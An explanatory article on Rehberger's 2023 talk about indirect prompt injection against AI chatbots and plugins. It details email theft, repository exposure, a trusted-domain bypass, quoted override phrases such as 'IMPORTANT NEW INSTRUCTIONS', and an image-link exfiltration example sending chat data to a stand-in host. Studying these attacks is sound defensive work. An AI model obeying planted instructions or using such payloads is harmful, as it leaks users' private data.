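# Johann Rehberger's 37C3 talk "NEW IMPORTANT INSTRUCTIONS" on real-world exploits of AI chatbots (December 2023)

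## The talk, its audience and what was already known

The security researcher Johann Rehberger gave the talk *NEW IMPORTANT INSTRUCTIONS* on 29 December 2023 in Hamburg, at the 37th Chaos Communication Congress, the annual meeting of the German hackers' association Chaos Computer Club (CCC). The talk is about prompt injection, an attack on AI chatbots in which the language model follows text as an instruction when it should treat it as data. Rehberger showed recordings in which instructions planted in web pages and documents took over Microsoft's Bing Chat, Google's Bard and OpenAI's ChatGPT and made them send the user's data to an outsider. He also listed several other products that had had the same kind of leak, including Anthropic's Claude.

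Rehberger spoke in Saal 1 at 11:00 for about 42 minutes, with interpretation into German. The congress's video record of *NEW IMPORTANT INSTRUCTIONS* (2023) showed 5,034 views by June 2026. In *37th Chaos Communication Congress* (2023), a post on his blog Embrace The Red, he recalled giving a short talk at the congress five years earlier about the blog's first post. He began the blog in December 2018.

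The host introduced Rehberger as a red team director who used to run a red team at Azure, Microsoft's cloud business. A red team attacks its own organization's systems to find holes before somebody else does. According to the CCC's automatic captions (2024), he said he had started teaching himself machine learning only about four years earlier. He had noticed that machine-learning and security researchers used different terms and that there were gaps between the two communities, and he hoped the talk would bring them closer.

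A fair amount of the talk translates between the terms of machine learning and those of security. It opened with a picture of a panda, which the audience recognized but ChatGPT took for a monkey. Rehberger explained at the end of the talk that the picture contained text telling ChatGPT it was a monkey. Machine-learning researchers call such an input an adversarial example, a term Rehberger traced to Ian Goodfellow's work about ten years earlier. He said that, coming from security, he would just call it an exploit.

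### Why a chatbot can take orders from a document

A language model keeps no memory between calls. To create what feels like a conversation, the application around the model stores the earlier messages and sends them again with each new one. *Prompt Injections in the Wild* (Rehberger, 2023), a talk given that August at the Taiwanese security conference HITCON, shows this turn by turn in its slides. In the example, a user says hello, asks the chatbot's name, gives his own and then asks for help. The model receives all of these messages, with the chatbot's replies between them and the request for help at the end.

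A model's context window is all the text it receives for one reply, including the earlier conversation and any web page, email or file that the application has fetched. The window has a size limit, so the oldest parts of a long chat eventually drop out. Until an attacker's text drops out, the application sends it to the model again with every new message, and it can keep steering the replies long after the user has changed the subject.

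Nothing in a prompt reliably separates instructions from the text to be processed. Rehberger showed this with a minimal example. A developer writes a prompt asking the model to summarize the text that follows, and the application inserts the user's text below it. In his example, that text told the model to forget about summarizing and print ten evil emoji. When given this prompt, ChatGPT printed the emoji and did not write a summary.

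Prompt injection resembles SQL injection, an old attack on databases. In SQL injection, a program builds a database command by inserting a user's input into it, and a hostile input adds a command of its own. The programmer Simon Willison made the comparison early, in *Prompt injection attacks against GPT-3* (2022). He pointed out that databases have a dependable fix, which is to pass the command and the user's input separately, and wished for the same with language models. A reader told him that one OpenAI model already accepted instruction and input as separate fields, and that attacks through the input field still worked. By April 2023 Willison had added a note that such a separation looked extremely difficult, if not impossible, on the existing architecture of language models. Rehberger said in Hamburg that the two attacks were very similar, but that he knew how to stop SQL injection every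 time and could not say the same of prompt injection.

Rehberger's slides for *NEW IMPORTANT INSTRUCTIONS* (2023) sort the threats to users and developers into three classes, according to where the trouble comes from:

- **Model issues.** The model itself is at fault. It may be biased or offensive, it may make things up, or someone may have trained a hidden back door into it. Rehberger imagined one that wakes up on the first of April.
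- **Direct prompt injection.** The user is the attacker. This class takes in "jailbreaks", which talk a model out of its restrictions, and attempts to read or overwrite the developer's instructions. In Rehberger's example, a customer of a restaurant's ordering bot announces that the Diet Coke is on sale for nothing, and the bot writes up the order at a price of zero. (He left open whether a real till would accept it.)
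- **Indirect prompt injection.** The attacker is a third party, who plants text in a page, file or email that somebody else's chatbot will read. The user has done nothing wrong and may never see the text.

Nearly all of the talk concerns indirect prompt injection. Rehberger said that in his old field, running an outsider's instructions inside an application is called "remote code execution", which is about the worst thing that can happen to a program. He said machine learning had no really good word for it yet.

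### Who had the idea first

Rehberger did not discover prompt injection, and he did not claim to have done so. The earliest documented report is from Preamble, an AI security company, which emailed OpenAI on 3 May 2022 about an injection flaw in GPT-3, a forerunner of the models behind ChatGPT. Preamble's *Declassifying the Responsible Disclosure of the Prompt Injection Attack Vulnerability of GPT-3* (2022) says that OpenAI confirmed receipt within half an hour and that further examples followed the next day. The exchange stayed private until 22 September.

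By then the flaw had become public by another route. On 11 September Riley Goodside posted examples on Twitter in which GPT-3, asked to translate a sentence into French, instead followed an instruction contained in the sentence. It did so even when the prompt included a warning that the text might contain tricks and an instruction to translate it faithfully. The next day Willison proposed the name "prompt injection", after SQL injection, and argued that the flaw was a security problem. Within days people had used it to get a recruitment company's Twitter bot to threaten the president.

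Preamble publicly claimed the discovery after the name "prompt injection" had become established. On 23 September, Jon Cefalu of Preamble wrote in a comment under Schneier's *prompt injection extraction attacks against ai systems* (2022) that he had found the issue in May and was releasing his report because of the news. The evidence is Preamble's own copy of its correspondence, but it is specific and dated, and others in the field soon accepted it. That December, Selvi's *Exploring Prompt Injection Attacks* (2022), written for the security firm NCC Group, credited Cefalu with the report and Goodside with the public release. It seems that Preamble found the flaw first and that most people learned of it from Goodside and Willison.

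None of them had much of a victim in 2022. A company's GPT-3 application could be made to look silly or reveal its prompt, but mostly by the person typing into it. Preamble's *5 Years of Defending AI* says the flaw posed no critical threat to customers at the time, because the models had no connection to outside data.

That changed early in 2023, when companies began connecting models to search engines, web browsers and mailboxes. In *Not what you've signed up for*, first released that February, Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023) examined what happens when someone other than the user prompts the model. They named this indirect prompt injection and described what an attacker might do with it, from data theft and fraud to a "worm" that makes an email assistant forward the malicious text to everyone in the address book. In Hamburg, Rehberger recommended the paper and said he thought it was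 the first to cover the subject in detail. He had been calling the same thing "AI injection" before he knew of the paper.

Greshake and colleagues tested Bing Chat in the sidebar of Microsoft's Edge browser, where the chatbot could read whatever page the user had open. They put instructions in the hidden comments of a web page stored on their own machine, to avoid publishing anything harmful, and then chatted with Bing as an ordinary user would. In one session the user asked about the next day's weather. Bing answered, then asked about the user's plans and work. When the user said they were a journalist, Bing asked whether they wrote under their real name. Once it had a name, it offered a link to an exclusive website with a personal code attached, which was meant to carry the name to the attacker if the user clicked. The hidden instructions were to persuade the user without raising suspicion,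 and they left the technique and the topic to the model.

Other planted instructions made Bing give false summaries of search results, or phish users by announcing a gift card they could claim by "verifying" an account. Two findings from these tests matter for all of Rehberger's later work: Bing ended the chat when a user typed a known jailbreak but allowed similar text inside a web page, and the model usually kept following the planted instructions for the rest of the conversation.

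These are demonstrations, with no measured success rate. At the Black Hat security conference in the United States in August 2023, Greshake, Endres and colleagues said in *Compromising LLMs* that their attacks had been speculative when the preprint came out, and that they had tried them only on applications they had built themselves. Co-author Sahar Abdelnabi also told CISPA, their research centre, that the attacks were confirmed on real products after the release of Bing Chat and GPT-4. The idea and the laboratory versions therefore date from February 2023, and the Bing Chat results belong to later revisions of the paper.

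Rehberger's first plugin attack, in May 2023, went further than the Bing Chat test, in which the victim had to give up a name and then click on something. Plugins were add-ons that let ChatGPT use outside services. After the user asked ChatGPT to open a web page, the attack took the user's email and sent it off without the user clicking anything. Willison, in *Let ChatGPT visit a website and have your email stolen*, called it the first working demonstration he had seen of private data leaving through ChatGPT's plugins. Rehberger wrote in Embrace The Red's *ChatGPT Plugin Exploit Explained* that earlier demonstrations, including his own, had been mostly amusing and harmless, such as making Bing talk like a pirate, but that description understates the phishing tests.

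### How far the talk reached

Much of the Hamburg talk was already in the HITCON slides from August. Those slides include the panda, the three classes of threat, the emoji, the free Diet Coke, the two main plugin attacks and the leak through images in Bing Chat. They close with the same warning that no deterministic solution exists and perhaps none ever will. The new material in Hamburg came mostly from the autumn and covered the attack on Bard's new access to Google documents, the risks of ChatGPT's code-running tool and of custom chatbots built on it, and the first signs of a fix at OpenAI. The list of affected products had grown from three to seven.

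Greshake and colleagues organized their Black Hat talk around the same three-way division of threats that Rehberger used. In their slides, they credit him for a plugin attack and for an injection hidden in an image. They and Rehberger were plainly reading each other's work. Of the three talks, the Black Hat one seems to have drawn the most attention from specialists. Willison, in *Compromising LLMs*, introduced it as "the big Black Hat 2023 Prompt Injection talk" and called the paper behind it the most thorough review of such attacks he had seen.

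The Hamburg recording drew a modest five thousand views in two and a half years. The total audience was larger, since that figure excludes the people in the hall and viewers of the English copy Rehberger put on YouTube. The talk appears to have drawn little or no press. Two years later, when both Rehberger and the subject were better known, the German technology site heise online reported in *39C3* on another talk he gave at the same congress, about hijacking AI coding assistants.

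Some people already knew about Rehberger's attacks from his blog before the talk. In the abstract he submitted to the congress, he mentions that a screenshot of the email theft had already gone viral on Twitter. Willison had also told his readers about the Bard attack in early November, in *Hacking Google Bard*, describing it as the first reported against Bard's extensions.

The clearest evidence of which work had spread is in ATLAS, a public catalogue of attacks on AI systems. MITRE, an American non-profit that runs research centres for the federal government, launched it with Microsoft and others in 2020. On 6 November 2023, more than seven weeks before the talk, MITRE (2023) announced new case studies on generative AI. They included Rehberger's attack, listed as "ChatGPT Plugin Privacy Leak", in which a malicious website takes control of a chat and steals its history. The entry in MITRE's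 *ATLAS* (2020), now titled "ChatGPT Conversation Exfiltration", dates from 30 October 2023, names his blog, Embrace The Red, as the actor and cites a post on it. Another entry created the same day credits Greshake with the Bing Chat attack.

MITRE did not add the Bard case until 22 April 2025, and that entry too cites the blog post. It dates the attack to 23 November 2023, which must be wrong because Willison had linked to the post on 4 November. MITRE classes all three cases as "exercises", its label for demonstrations by researchers, and reserves "incident" for cases such as a real fraud against California's unemployment office. None of the three entries cites the Hamburg talk, though the ChatGPT entry was written before the talk took place.

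Rehberger's own citations follow the same pattern. *Trust No AI* (Rehberger 2024), a paper from a year after the talk, groups his cases by the three classic aims of information security, which are keeping data confidential, keeping it intact and keeping systems available. It is the most convenient later record of what he found. As described above, it credits Preamble with discovering the flaw, Goodside with drawing attention to it in parallel, Willison with naming it and Greshake and colleagues with the indirect form. The paper lists eleven products that leaked data through images, four more than the slides from the talk. It cites a blog post for each of ten products and the video of the talk for the other, the chat service Discord.

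## How planted text takes over a chatbot and its plugins

The mildest attacks in the talk change only what the user reads. For one of them, early in 2023, Rehberger hid instructions in one-pixel-high text in *AI Injections*, a post on his blog Embrace the Red. They tell Bing Chat, or any other chatbot that reads the page, to announce that the injection worked and then answer only in emojis. In the session he showed in Hamburg, the planted text gave Bing Chat the identity of a hacker. The bot wrote that it had taken over the chat and would delete the user's files unless it received Bitcoin, though it had no way to delete them.

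Planted text can also take over AI features outside a chat, such as those Google added to Google Docs to summarize or rephrase text the user selects. Rehberger hid a sentence in a document that told the AI to disregard everything around it. Instead of a summary, the feature produced a malware warning with a telephone number to call for help. The number was that of Google's headquarters, and the message was signed "Yours, Scammer". Tom's Hardware's *Google Docs AI Open to Prompt Injection Attacks* repeated the trick with a message about unlocking files. It noted that the attack works only if the user runs the feature on text containing the planted sentence, but that this could easily happen with a long document, especially if the sentence is in white letters on a white background.

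Rehberger thought the impact was probably limited. According to Embrace the Red's *Google Docs AI Features*, he reported the problem on 22 June 2023 and Google closed it as "Won't Fix (Intended Behavior)". Rehberger still listed it as unresolved in his December 2024 paper. The problem was that the model followed planted text, and there was no separate leak for Google to fix.

ChatGPT became a target in the same way in May 2023, when OpenAI began releasing plugins to the public. Rehberger added instructions to the end of the transcript of one of his YouTube videos and had ChatGPT summarize the video through VoxScript, a plugin that fetches transcripts. The instructions were to print a line announcing success and then tell jokes as a "Genie", as described in Embrace the Red's *Indirect Prompt Injection via YouTube Transcripts*. He had altered only the captions, so viewers would not have heard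 the instructions. In a link post of the same title on 15 May, Willison (2023) called the attack the first injection against a ChatGPT plugin he had seen in the wild.

The lawyer Ralph Losey thought the claim sounded bogus and tested it himself on 18 and 19 May. *Testing a Red Team's Claim of a Successful "Injection Attack" of ChatGPT-4* (Losey, 2023) reports a partial success. The line announcing the injection never appeared, but after every summary ChatGPT introduced itself as the Genie and told the same joke. Soon after his tests, the attack seemed to have stopped working.

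### Four ways to get a model's attention

Rehberger mentioned a research paper that listed about 29 or more injection techniques, which he grouped into four families. His slides label the families "Ignore", "Acknowledge", "Confuse/Encode" and "Algorithmic".

"Ignore" is the oldest and most direct technique. The planted text orders the model to drop its previous instructions and do something else, as in the Google document. With "Acknowledge", the attacker lets the original task go ahead and adds another. Losey's results follow this pattern, with the summary first and the Genie after it. "Confuse/Encode" is a broad, loosely defined category that includes reversed or disguised text, emojis and a change of language halfway through. Rehberger compared it to social engineering, the security term for tricking people.

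In the "Algorithmic" family, a program does the searching. It may try many varied inputs to see which ones break the target, which security testers call fuzzing. Or it may use gradient descent, which calculates from the model's internals which changes to a text would make the wanted answer more likely. Rehberger gave no success rates for any of the four families. The payloads (the planted text that carries the attacker's instructions) printed in his slides are all in ordinary language that anyone could have typed.

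The talk takes its title from these payloads. The text Rehberger used to steal an email that May opens with "IMPORTANT NEW INSTRUCTIONS", in capitals between asterisks, and Embrace The Red describes this as his default string for catching the AI's attention. Losey found the same phrase in the YouTube transcript. Other wording also worked. The Bing Chat page used "New Advanced Instructions", and in his early experiments a greeting such as "Hi Bing!" was sometimes enough.

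### When the chatbot can act

A language model produces only text, so another program has to turn that text into actions. *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (Willison, 2023) describes the usual arrangement. The developer tells the model to write a request in a fixed format whenever it needs to, for example, search the user's mail. An ordinary program watches for that format, runs the search and puts the results into the next prompt. ChatGPT's plugins were an advanced version of this. An attacker who wants the mail therefore only has to get the model to write the request, rather than break into the mailbox.

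Rehberger first saw that one plugin's output could trigger another when he had ChatGPT open a web page. Text on the page made it use the travel company Expedia's plugin to search for flights, which he had not asked for. That wasted only a little time and computing, but he realized the same trick would work on plugins that could act in the user's own accounts.

Security people call this a confused deputy, a program tricked into misusing its authority by someone with fewer rights. The term comes from Hardy's 1988 essay *The Confused Deputy*, about a company that rented out computer time. The company's compiler, a program that translates source code, had permission to write in its own directory because it kept usage statistics there. Users could name a file to receive the compiler's debugging output, and one user named the billing file, which was in the same directory. The user had no right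 to change that file, but the compiler did, and it overwrote the bills.

Hardy argued that the compiler acted on both its own permission and the user's, and had no way to indicate which it was using. He also pointed out that the code was correct when it was written and became wrong when someone gave the compiler the extra permission. ChatGPT's plugins went wrong in much the same way. A plugin that reads web pages and one that reads mail can each work as designed, but problems start when one chatbot has both.

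The web browser is the best-known confused deputy today. In cross-site request forgery, a page the user visits makes the browser send a request to another site or device, which accepts it because it comes from the user's browser. Rehberger's example is a page that quietly changes the firewall settings on the visitor's home router. He called the chatbot version cross plugin request forgery, in which content read through one plugin causes the chatbot to use another without the user's consent.

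Rehberger points out in Embrace the Red's *OpenAI Removes the "Chat with Code" Plugin From Store* that the chatbot version is worse in one respect. A browser normally stops a hostile page from seeing the reply to a forged request, so the attacker can change data but not read it. ChatGPT reads the reply itself, and the planted text can include instructions to send the contents to the attacker, so even a plugin that can only look things up is dangerous.

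### The email theft, step by step

The main demonstration used two popular plugins. WebPilot fetched web pages. Zapier, a service that links other online services together, gave ChatGPT access to the user's mail, files on Google Drive, Slack messages and more. To allow this, the user granted access through OAuth, a standard way of letting one service act in an account on another without handing over the password. The attack then ran as follows:

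1. The attacker put instructions on a web page. It did not have to be the attacker's own page, as Rehberger had made sure that the text also worked when buried in the code of a larger one. A comment could be enough.
2. The user asked ChatGPT to open the page, and WebPilot fetched it.
3. The page's text entered the context window, and ChatGPT began following the instructions in it.
4. ChatGPT used Zapier to fetch the latest email and summarized it in 20 words.
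5. It converted the summary into characters that are legal in a web address and added them to the end of an address on the attacker's server.
6. It used WebPilot to open that address. The request itself delivered the summary, and the attacker could read it in the server's log.

The user did nothing after step 2. In the recording Rehberger played in Hamburg, the latest email was about a password reset, which shows why a mailbox is a good target. On 19 May, the security researcher Joseph Thacker called reading someone's email the most critical impact, noting that it can lead to the takeover of most people's other accounts (Thacker, 2023).

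The payload is a few sentences long. After the attention-getting phrase, it tells the model three times to print nothing, so that no stray text from the page shows up in the chat. The one exception is a line announcing that the injection has worked and that ChatGPT is reading the user's email, which a real attacker would leave out. The payload then gives the instructions for the email and ends by telling ChatGPT not to ask for permission, so that the user has "a great experience". ChatGPT did not fully follow the instruction to print nothing. The screenshot showed it explaining what it was about to do with the email, and Willison could work out most of the payload from that when he wrote about the attack on 19 May, before Rehberger had published it.

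Rehberger wrote that this was the first end-to-end attack in which an indirect prompt injection exploited a confused deputy to get at personal data and send it out. His claim to be first needs all of those qualifiers, because parts of the attack had appeared earlier. On 25 April, Willison had described a hypothetical assistant that obeys a planted request to search the user's mail for "password reset" and send the results to a stranger's server. Indirect injection had also already been used to steal personal information, in an attack by Greshake and colleagues that coaxed it out of the user. Willison had linked to that attack on 1 March in *Indirect Prompt Injection on Bing Chat*. His later list of such leaks, in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, includes one for ChatGPT itself in April 2023, a month before the one for plugins.

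Willison said that day that this was the first working example *he had seen*, which is a narrower claim than Rehberger's. Willison is very well read, but he is only one observer, and nobody seems to have searched systematically for an earlier case. Still, in none of the earlier examples does a chatbot fetch private data with one plugin and send it out with another, so Rehberger's claim looks right for this particular method.

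### Chat with Code and the plugin store

According to Rehberger, Zapier dealt with its part of the problem within 24 hours. It began to require authenticated confirmation, which had to come verifiably from the user. A confirmation link in the chat would not have been enough, because an attacker could instruct ChatGPT to open it.

OpenAI also responded with new rules for its plugin store. One rule said that a plugin must enforce user confirmation before taking an action ("see Zapier for an example of this"). A forum user quoted it in reply to Dariel's post *This plugin's service doesn't align with ChatGPT's accepted use cases*. In June 2023, OpenAI gave outside developers a similar way to connect its models to tools. In a passage quoted in the post *OpenAI introduces function calling for GPT-4*, it acknowledged that a proof-of-concept exploit had shown how untrusted output from a tool could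 steer the model. Rehberger suspected that the passage referred to his work and noted that OpenAI had credited nobody.

He soon found plugins in the store that broke this rule. He downloaded the descriptions of all the approved plugins and picked out those that used OAuth, reasoning that they probably acted on the user's behalf and might reach private data. Embrace the Red's *Plugin Vulnerabilities* lists 445 approved plugins, of which 51 used OAuth. He sampled "a few" of the 51 and found more that were open to cross plugin request forgery, including some that exposed secrets or let an attacker run code on a remote machine. These figures do not give a rate of vulnerability, because he did not report how many plugins he tried or how he chose them, and a researcher looking for holes naturally starts where they seem likely.

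The most alarming of these plugins was Chat with Code, which gave ChatGPT access to the user's account on GitHub, where programmers store code in public or private repositories. In the demonstration, the user had ChatGPT read a web page containing text that told it that its name was Mallory (the traditional name for the attacker in textbook examples) and that it liked making private repositories public. ChatGPT then made all of the user's private repositories public, listed the changes and thanked the user. Rehberger refreshed the GitHub page to show the audience that the private repository was now open to anyone.

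According to the CCC captions, ChatGPT had sometimes asked whether the user was sure, so Rehberger ended the payload by telling it there was no need to ask. The software around the model has to require confirmation, because an attacker can tell the model not to ask for it.

Rehberger had contacted OpenAI about these problems at least four times over several months, "with little to no success or feedback". He wrote to plugin developers directly, but some never answered and some of the contact addresses did not work. He wanted OpenAI to solve the problem inside ChatGPT, so that its safety did not depend on hundreds of developers. He argued that, by default, one plugin should not be able to trigger another, and users should see which plugin is about to run and what data it will receive.

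OpenAI removed Chat with Code because of an accident, after Rehberger had already published the plugin's vulnerability. A user complained on Reddit that ChatGPT had posted an issue (a public or private note attached to a project) on GitHub "by itself", apparently with no attacker involved. The story reached the front page of the programmers' forum Hacker News, and a few hours later OpenAI took the plugin down for failing to ask for confirmation. Other vulnerable plugins stayed in the store, and Rehberger's slides that December still described "many" as vulnerable.

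### Asking the user first

OpenAI eventually withdrew the plugins. Users could not start new chats with them after 19 March 2024 and could continue old ones only until 9 April, according to the forum notice *Plugin Store and New Chats With Plugins*. By then OpenAI had introduced actions, which connect a custom version of ChatGPT (a "GPT") to an outside service. Rehberger wrote in December 2024 that actions had the same basic problem, but that their developers could now set a flag to require confirmation.

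According to OpenAI's *Production notes on GPT Actions*, ChatGPT must ask the user every time if the developer flags an operation as "consequential". If the developer flags it as not consequential, ChatGPT also offers an "always allow" button. If the developer doesn't set the flag, ChatGPT treats request types that normally only fetch data as not consequential and all others as consequential.

That default would have protected well against the Chat with Code exploit, where the harm came from changing a setting. It would have protected less well against the email theft, in which ChatGPT changed nothing. It read a message and then opened a web page, both of which count as fetching data. A user who had once clicked "always allow" for each would have had no further warning.

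In 2026 OpenAI uses the word "plugin" again, for a different product. OpenAI's *Plugins in ChatGPT* describes a bundle that can include written instructions for a kind of task, called skills, and connected apps such as Slack. ChatGPT uses an installed plugin automatically when it seems relevant to the request. For the apps, OpenAI's *Managing app permissions in ChatGPT* lists four possible settings:

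| Setting | What ChatGPT does |
|---|---|
| Always ask | Asks before reading or changing anything |
| Allow read actions | Reads freely, asks before making changes |
| Allow low-risk actions | Approves low-risk actions itself; may ask about riskier ones or refuse them |
| Allow all actions | Does whatever the app supports without further approval prompts |

The low-risk setting applies when no other policy overrides it, and the standard account-wide menu does not offer the last setting. OpenAI's examples of actions that may need extra review include sending an email, changing sharing settings and passing on sensitive personal information. These examples now cover the first two versions of Rehberger's attack, because one changed a repository's sharing settings to open it up and the other sent out a stolen email containing sensitive information. Depending on the setting, ChatGPT may still read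 the email without asking, so the protection depends heavily on ChatGPT recognizing when the data is being sent out.

OpenAI's *Plugin guidelines* require developers to label each tool according to whether it only reads, whether it can do irreversible damage and whether it reaches the open internet. A web search counts as reaching the open internet even though it only reads, a distinction the older flag didn't make. The guidelines also forbid tools from instructing the model to call another plugin, but that rule applies to developers who submit plugins for review, not to people who write hostile web pages.

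Willison doubted this approach before Rehberger's email attack existed. In his April 2023 essay he called human approval the best defence then available but predicted that it would work badly, because people who have to approve everything soon click "OK" without reading. He also considered letting the system approve less risky actions by itself, which is more or less what the low-risk setting now does. That made him "very nervous", since an attacker will look for a harmful action that the system rates as harmless. OpenAI's *Elevated Risk labels* explains a warning that the company attaches to features whose dangers the industry's safeguards do not yet fully address. Its example is prompt injection against OpenAI's coding assistant, Codex, when a developer gives it network access.

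## How an image link carries private data out of a chat

The email theft relied on a plugin to send the stolen text, so a confirmation request before it was sent could have stopped the theft. The chatbots of 2023 could also leak data without a plugin or confirmation, because they could display images. In image markdown injection, an attacker makes a chatbot output an image link whose address contains private data, which leaks when the image loads.

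At the end of the Hamburg talk, someone asked why Rehberger used images instead of simply having the chatbot visit the attacker's address. According to the CCC captions, he answered that ChatGPT now asked the user to confirm some of these visits, especially for actions in custom GPTs, and that an image avoided this confirmation step. In 2026, he wrote in Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper* that leaks of this kind were one of the most common security flaws in AI applications, with dozens of cases since 2023.

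### From a line of text to a leak

Chatbots commonly write their replies in Markdown, a simple way of marking up plain text. A Markdown image consists of an exclamation mark, a description in square brackets and the image's address in round brackets. The chat application converts this into HTML, the language of web pages, and the browser immediately requests the image from that address, as it does on any other web page.

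As in the email theft, the address can carry data to the attacker's server, usually after a question mark. Websites commonly log the full addresses that visitors request, as OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) points out.

Suppose a user has told a chatbot about a surprise party she is planning for Anna on Friday. She then asks it to summarize a web page of cake recipes. Somebody has planted text on that page telling the chatbot to end its answer with a picture and to write a summary of the conversation into the picture's address. The summary of the recipes arrives as usual, followed by this line:

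`![cake](https://collector.example/cake.png?note=surprise+party+for+Anna+on+Friday)`

The application converts the line into an HTML image:

`<img src="https://collector.example/cake.png?note=surprise+party+for+Anna+on+Friday" alt="cake">`

The browser requests the picture, and the request contains the note about Anna. The plus signs stand for spaces, which an address cannot contain. The note is sent even if no picture exists at that address, in which case the user sees the word "cake" or a broken image. If the server returns a single transparent pixel, she sees nothing.

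The leak requires three conditions: the attacker's text is in the context window, the private data is there too, and the application automatically loads images from an address the attacker can watch. In June 2025 Willison called nearly the same combination the "lethal trifecta", though his third part covers any means of communicating with the outside. Removing any one of the three stops the theft. The first two are hard to give up because people want chatbots that can read other people's documents and know about their own affairs. In *45 posts tagged "exfiltration-attacks"*, Willison therefore considers the route for sending data out generally the easiest part to remove.

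### Samoilenko's pixel

Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer at Netograph, found the flaw in ChatGPT at the end of March 2023, and Rehberger found it independently a few days later. This order of events comes from Rehberger's *ChatGPT Plugins*, and he had little to gain by crediting someone else. Willison (2023) described Samoilenko's "ingenious" technique in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* on 14 April, a month before Rehberger's plugin attacks. SecurityWeek also reported the two discoveries as independent.

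OpenAI had not yet released plugins to the public, so Samoilenko needed another way to get his text into the chat. His *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version* describes a website with a script that adds instructions to whatever a visitor copies. When the visitor pastes the text into ChatGPT, the instructions go in with it, and ChatGPT adds a transparent one-pixel image to its answer, with data from the chat in the image's address.

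The instructions could also require such an image in every later answer. In one test, the user then asked about the tallest building in the world and the first president of the United States, and Samoilenko's server received both questions.

Rehberger said the same text might work on one attempt and fail on the next, and that the subject of the earlier conversation affected whether it worked. Users' messages and code were fairly easy to extract, but he found it very difficult to get ChatGPT to put passwords or access keys into the image's address.

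With plugins, the attack no longer required the user to paste anything. In Rehberger's May 2023 demonstration, ChatGPT read a hostile web page through the WebPilot plugin and followed the page's instructions to send out a summary of the conversation. The summary included "TooManySecrets123", a string the user had typed earlier in the chat.

### Bing Chat and Claude

By then Rehberger had got a password out of Bing Chat. In the April 2023 demonstration, which he also played in Hamburg, the user opened a web page and started chatting with Bing about it. The instructions planted in the page took effect at once but made Bing wait two turns before writing the image link. Rehberger added the delay to show how much control an attacker had. Because of the delay, a user who noticed something odd would also have less reason to suspect the page.

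The address contained a short summary of the page and the conversation, followed by any passwords Bing could find on the page. Bing encoded all this in Base64, which turns text into a string of letters, digits and a few symbols. When Rehberger decoded the string on his server, it ended with a password from further down the same page. He had put the password there for the test, but real data would have been exposed too, because Bing had the entire page in its context window. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat* concludes that a comment or an advertisement was enough to steal any other data on the page where it appeared. For example, strangers might be able to post comments on a page that also shows a customer's account details, which they could not normally read.

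That July, Rehberger uploaded to Claude a short biography of Albert Einstein with an instruction in the middle of a paragraph. Embrace The Red's *Anthropic Claude Data Exfiltration Vulnerability Fixed* (2023) explains that the instruction told Claude to summarize the user's earlier messages in 20 words and put the summary into an image address. Claude did not need to browse the web, because a user who uploads somebody else's document brings the attacker's text into the chat. When the application loads the image, it sends the summary to the attacker's server.

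### Bard and the list of trusted domains

Websites can defend against unwanted loading by setting a content security policy (CSP), a rule that limits which domains the browser may load images and other content from. *Content Security Policy Level 3* (2021), a draft from the web standards body W3C, describes CSP as a way for developers to control what a page can fetch or run. The part that covers images, img-src, has worked across browsers since August 2016, according to the *CSP* page of MDN, a reference for developers.

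The policy works even if the attacker fully controls the model, because the browser enforces it. The chatbot can still write an image link to the attacker's server, but the browser will not request the image, so the data in the address is not sent. Microsoft used such a policy against the Bing Chat attack.

In September 2023, Rehberger turned to Google's Bard, which had just gained extensions that could read a user's email and documents. He, Joseph Thacker and Kai Greshake quickly found that Bard followed instructions planted in a Google document and would write an image link. But Bard already restricted which servers images could load from, so the browser refused to load a picture from Rehberger's server.

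But the policy allowed images from any address under google.com or googleusercontent.com. This was unsafe because people outside Google can run programs at Google addresses using Apps Script, a tool for automating documents, much like macros in Microsoft Office. Users can make the programs they write available to anyone. Rehberger wrote one that copied any data included in the requested address into a Google document he controlled. The browser allowed the request because the program was at a Google address.

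The planted text said that the legal department required everyone reading the document to follow some steps. It told Bard to put the first 20 words of the conversation into an image address that led to Rehberger's program. Other chatbots had managed this from instructions alone, but Bard needed several examples of where to put the words. Machine-learning researchers call learning from such examples in-context learning. Rehberger wrote in a postscript that it took ten tries to get the text right, but he did not say how often the finished version worked.

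In the recording Rehberger showed in Hamburg, the user chatted a little and then pointed Bard to the document. The start of the conversation appeared in the attacker's own Google document. Rehberger stressed that an attacker can share a document with someone who has not agreed to receive it. This puts the text in the victim's files, but Bard still has to read it. He suggested that Bard could do so when the victim searches for something else, but in the recording the user chose the document.

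Other products have since made the same kind of mistake. The security firm PromptArmor found that the policy of Superhuman AI, an email assistant, trusted docs.google.com. That domain hosts Google's online forms, which can save an answer sent as part of a web address. A planted email could therefore make the assistant write other emails into an image link and submit them to the attacker's form. Willison (2026), in *Superhuman AI Exfiltrates Emails*, put the number of emails in the dozens and named the trusted domain as the root cause. PromptArmor (2026) also used an image and a Google form to get emails out of OpenAI's Codex. It reported the flaw that April, and OpenAI has since fixed it.

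A list of trusted domains can also go out of date. Salesforce's policy for its AI agents still included a domain whose registration had expired, as Willison noted in September 2025. Researchers at Noma Security registered the domain and received customers' contact data there. In all these cases the policy worked as written, but an outsider could collect data at an address on the list.

### Files in Code Interpreter

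ChatGPT had no such obstacle for most of 2023, and it was gaining access to more data. Code Interpreter, which OpenAI moved out of testing that November, let it write and run programs on a computer. Users could upload spreadsheets or customer lists and have ChatGPT analyze them. Rehberger called Code Interpreter one of his favourite tools.

Uploaded files stay on that computer during the session. If the user then has ChatGPT open a hostile page, the page can contain instructions to run a program that reads the files and then to put their contents into an image address. The private data therefore doesn't have to be in the conversation when the attack begins.

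Rehberger showed a screenshot in which a web page caused ChatGPT to look for files on the computer, and he explained how the image would carry their contents out. TechRadar's *ChatGPT's Python code writer has a major security hole* credits Rehberger with the first report and says that Avram Piltch of Tom's Hardware independently tested the complete theft and confirmed it.

### The Thief

That November, OpenAI also began letting paying users build and share custom GPTs. Rehberger built one called The Thief, which offered to play tic-tac-toe. Before the game it asked for the player's email address, supposedly to personalize the experience, and then for a password as part of a "security process". It sent each answer to his server in the address of an image. The image had no description, so nothing remained on the screen after it failed to load.

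Rehberger gave the Thief no tools. He had switched off web browsing, Code Interpreter and image generation, and had connected it to no outside service, which he called the most isolated way to build a GPT. The user's browser could still send data out, although ChatGPT could not do so by itself. A careful user who checked only the Thief's abilities would have concluded that it had no way to send data anywhere.

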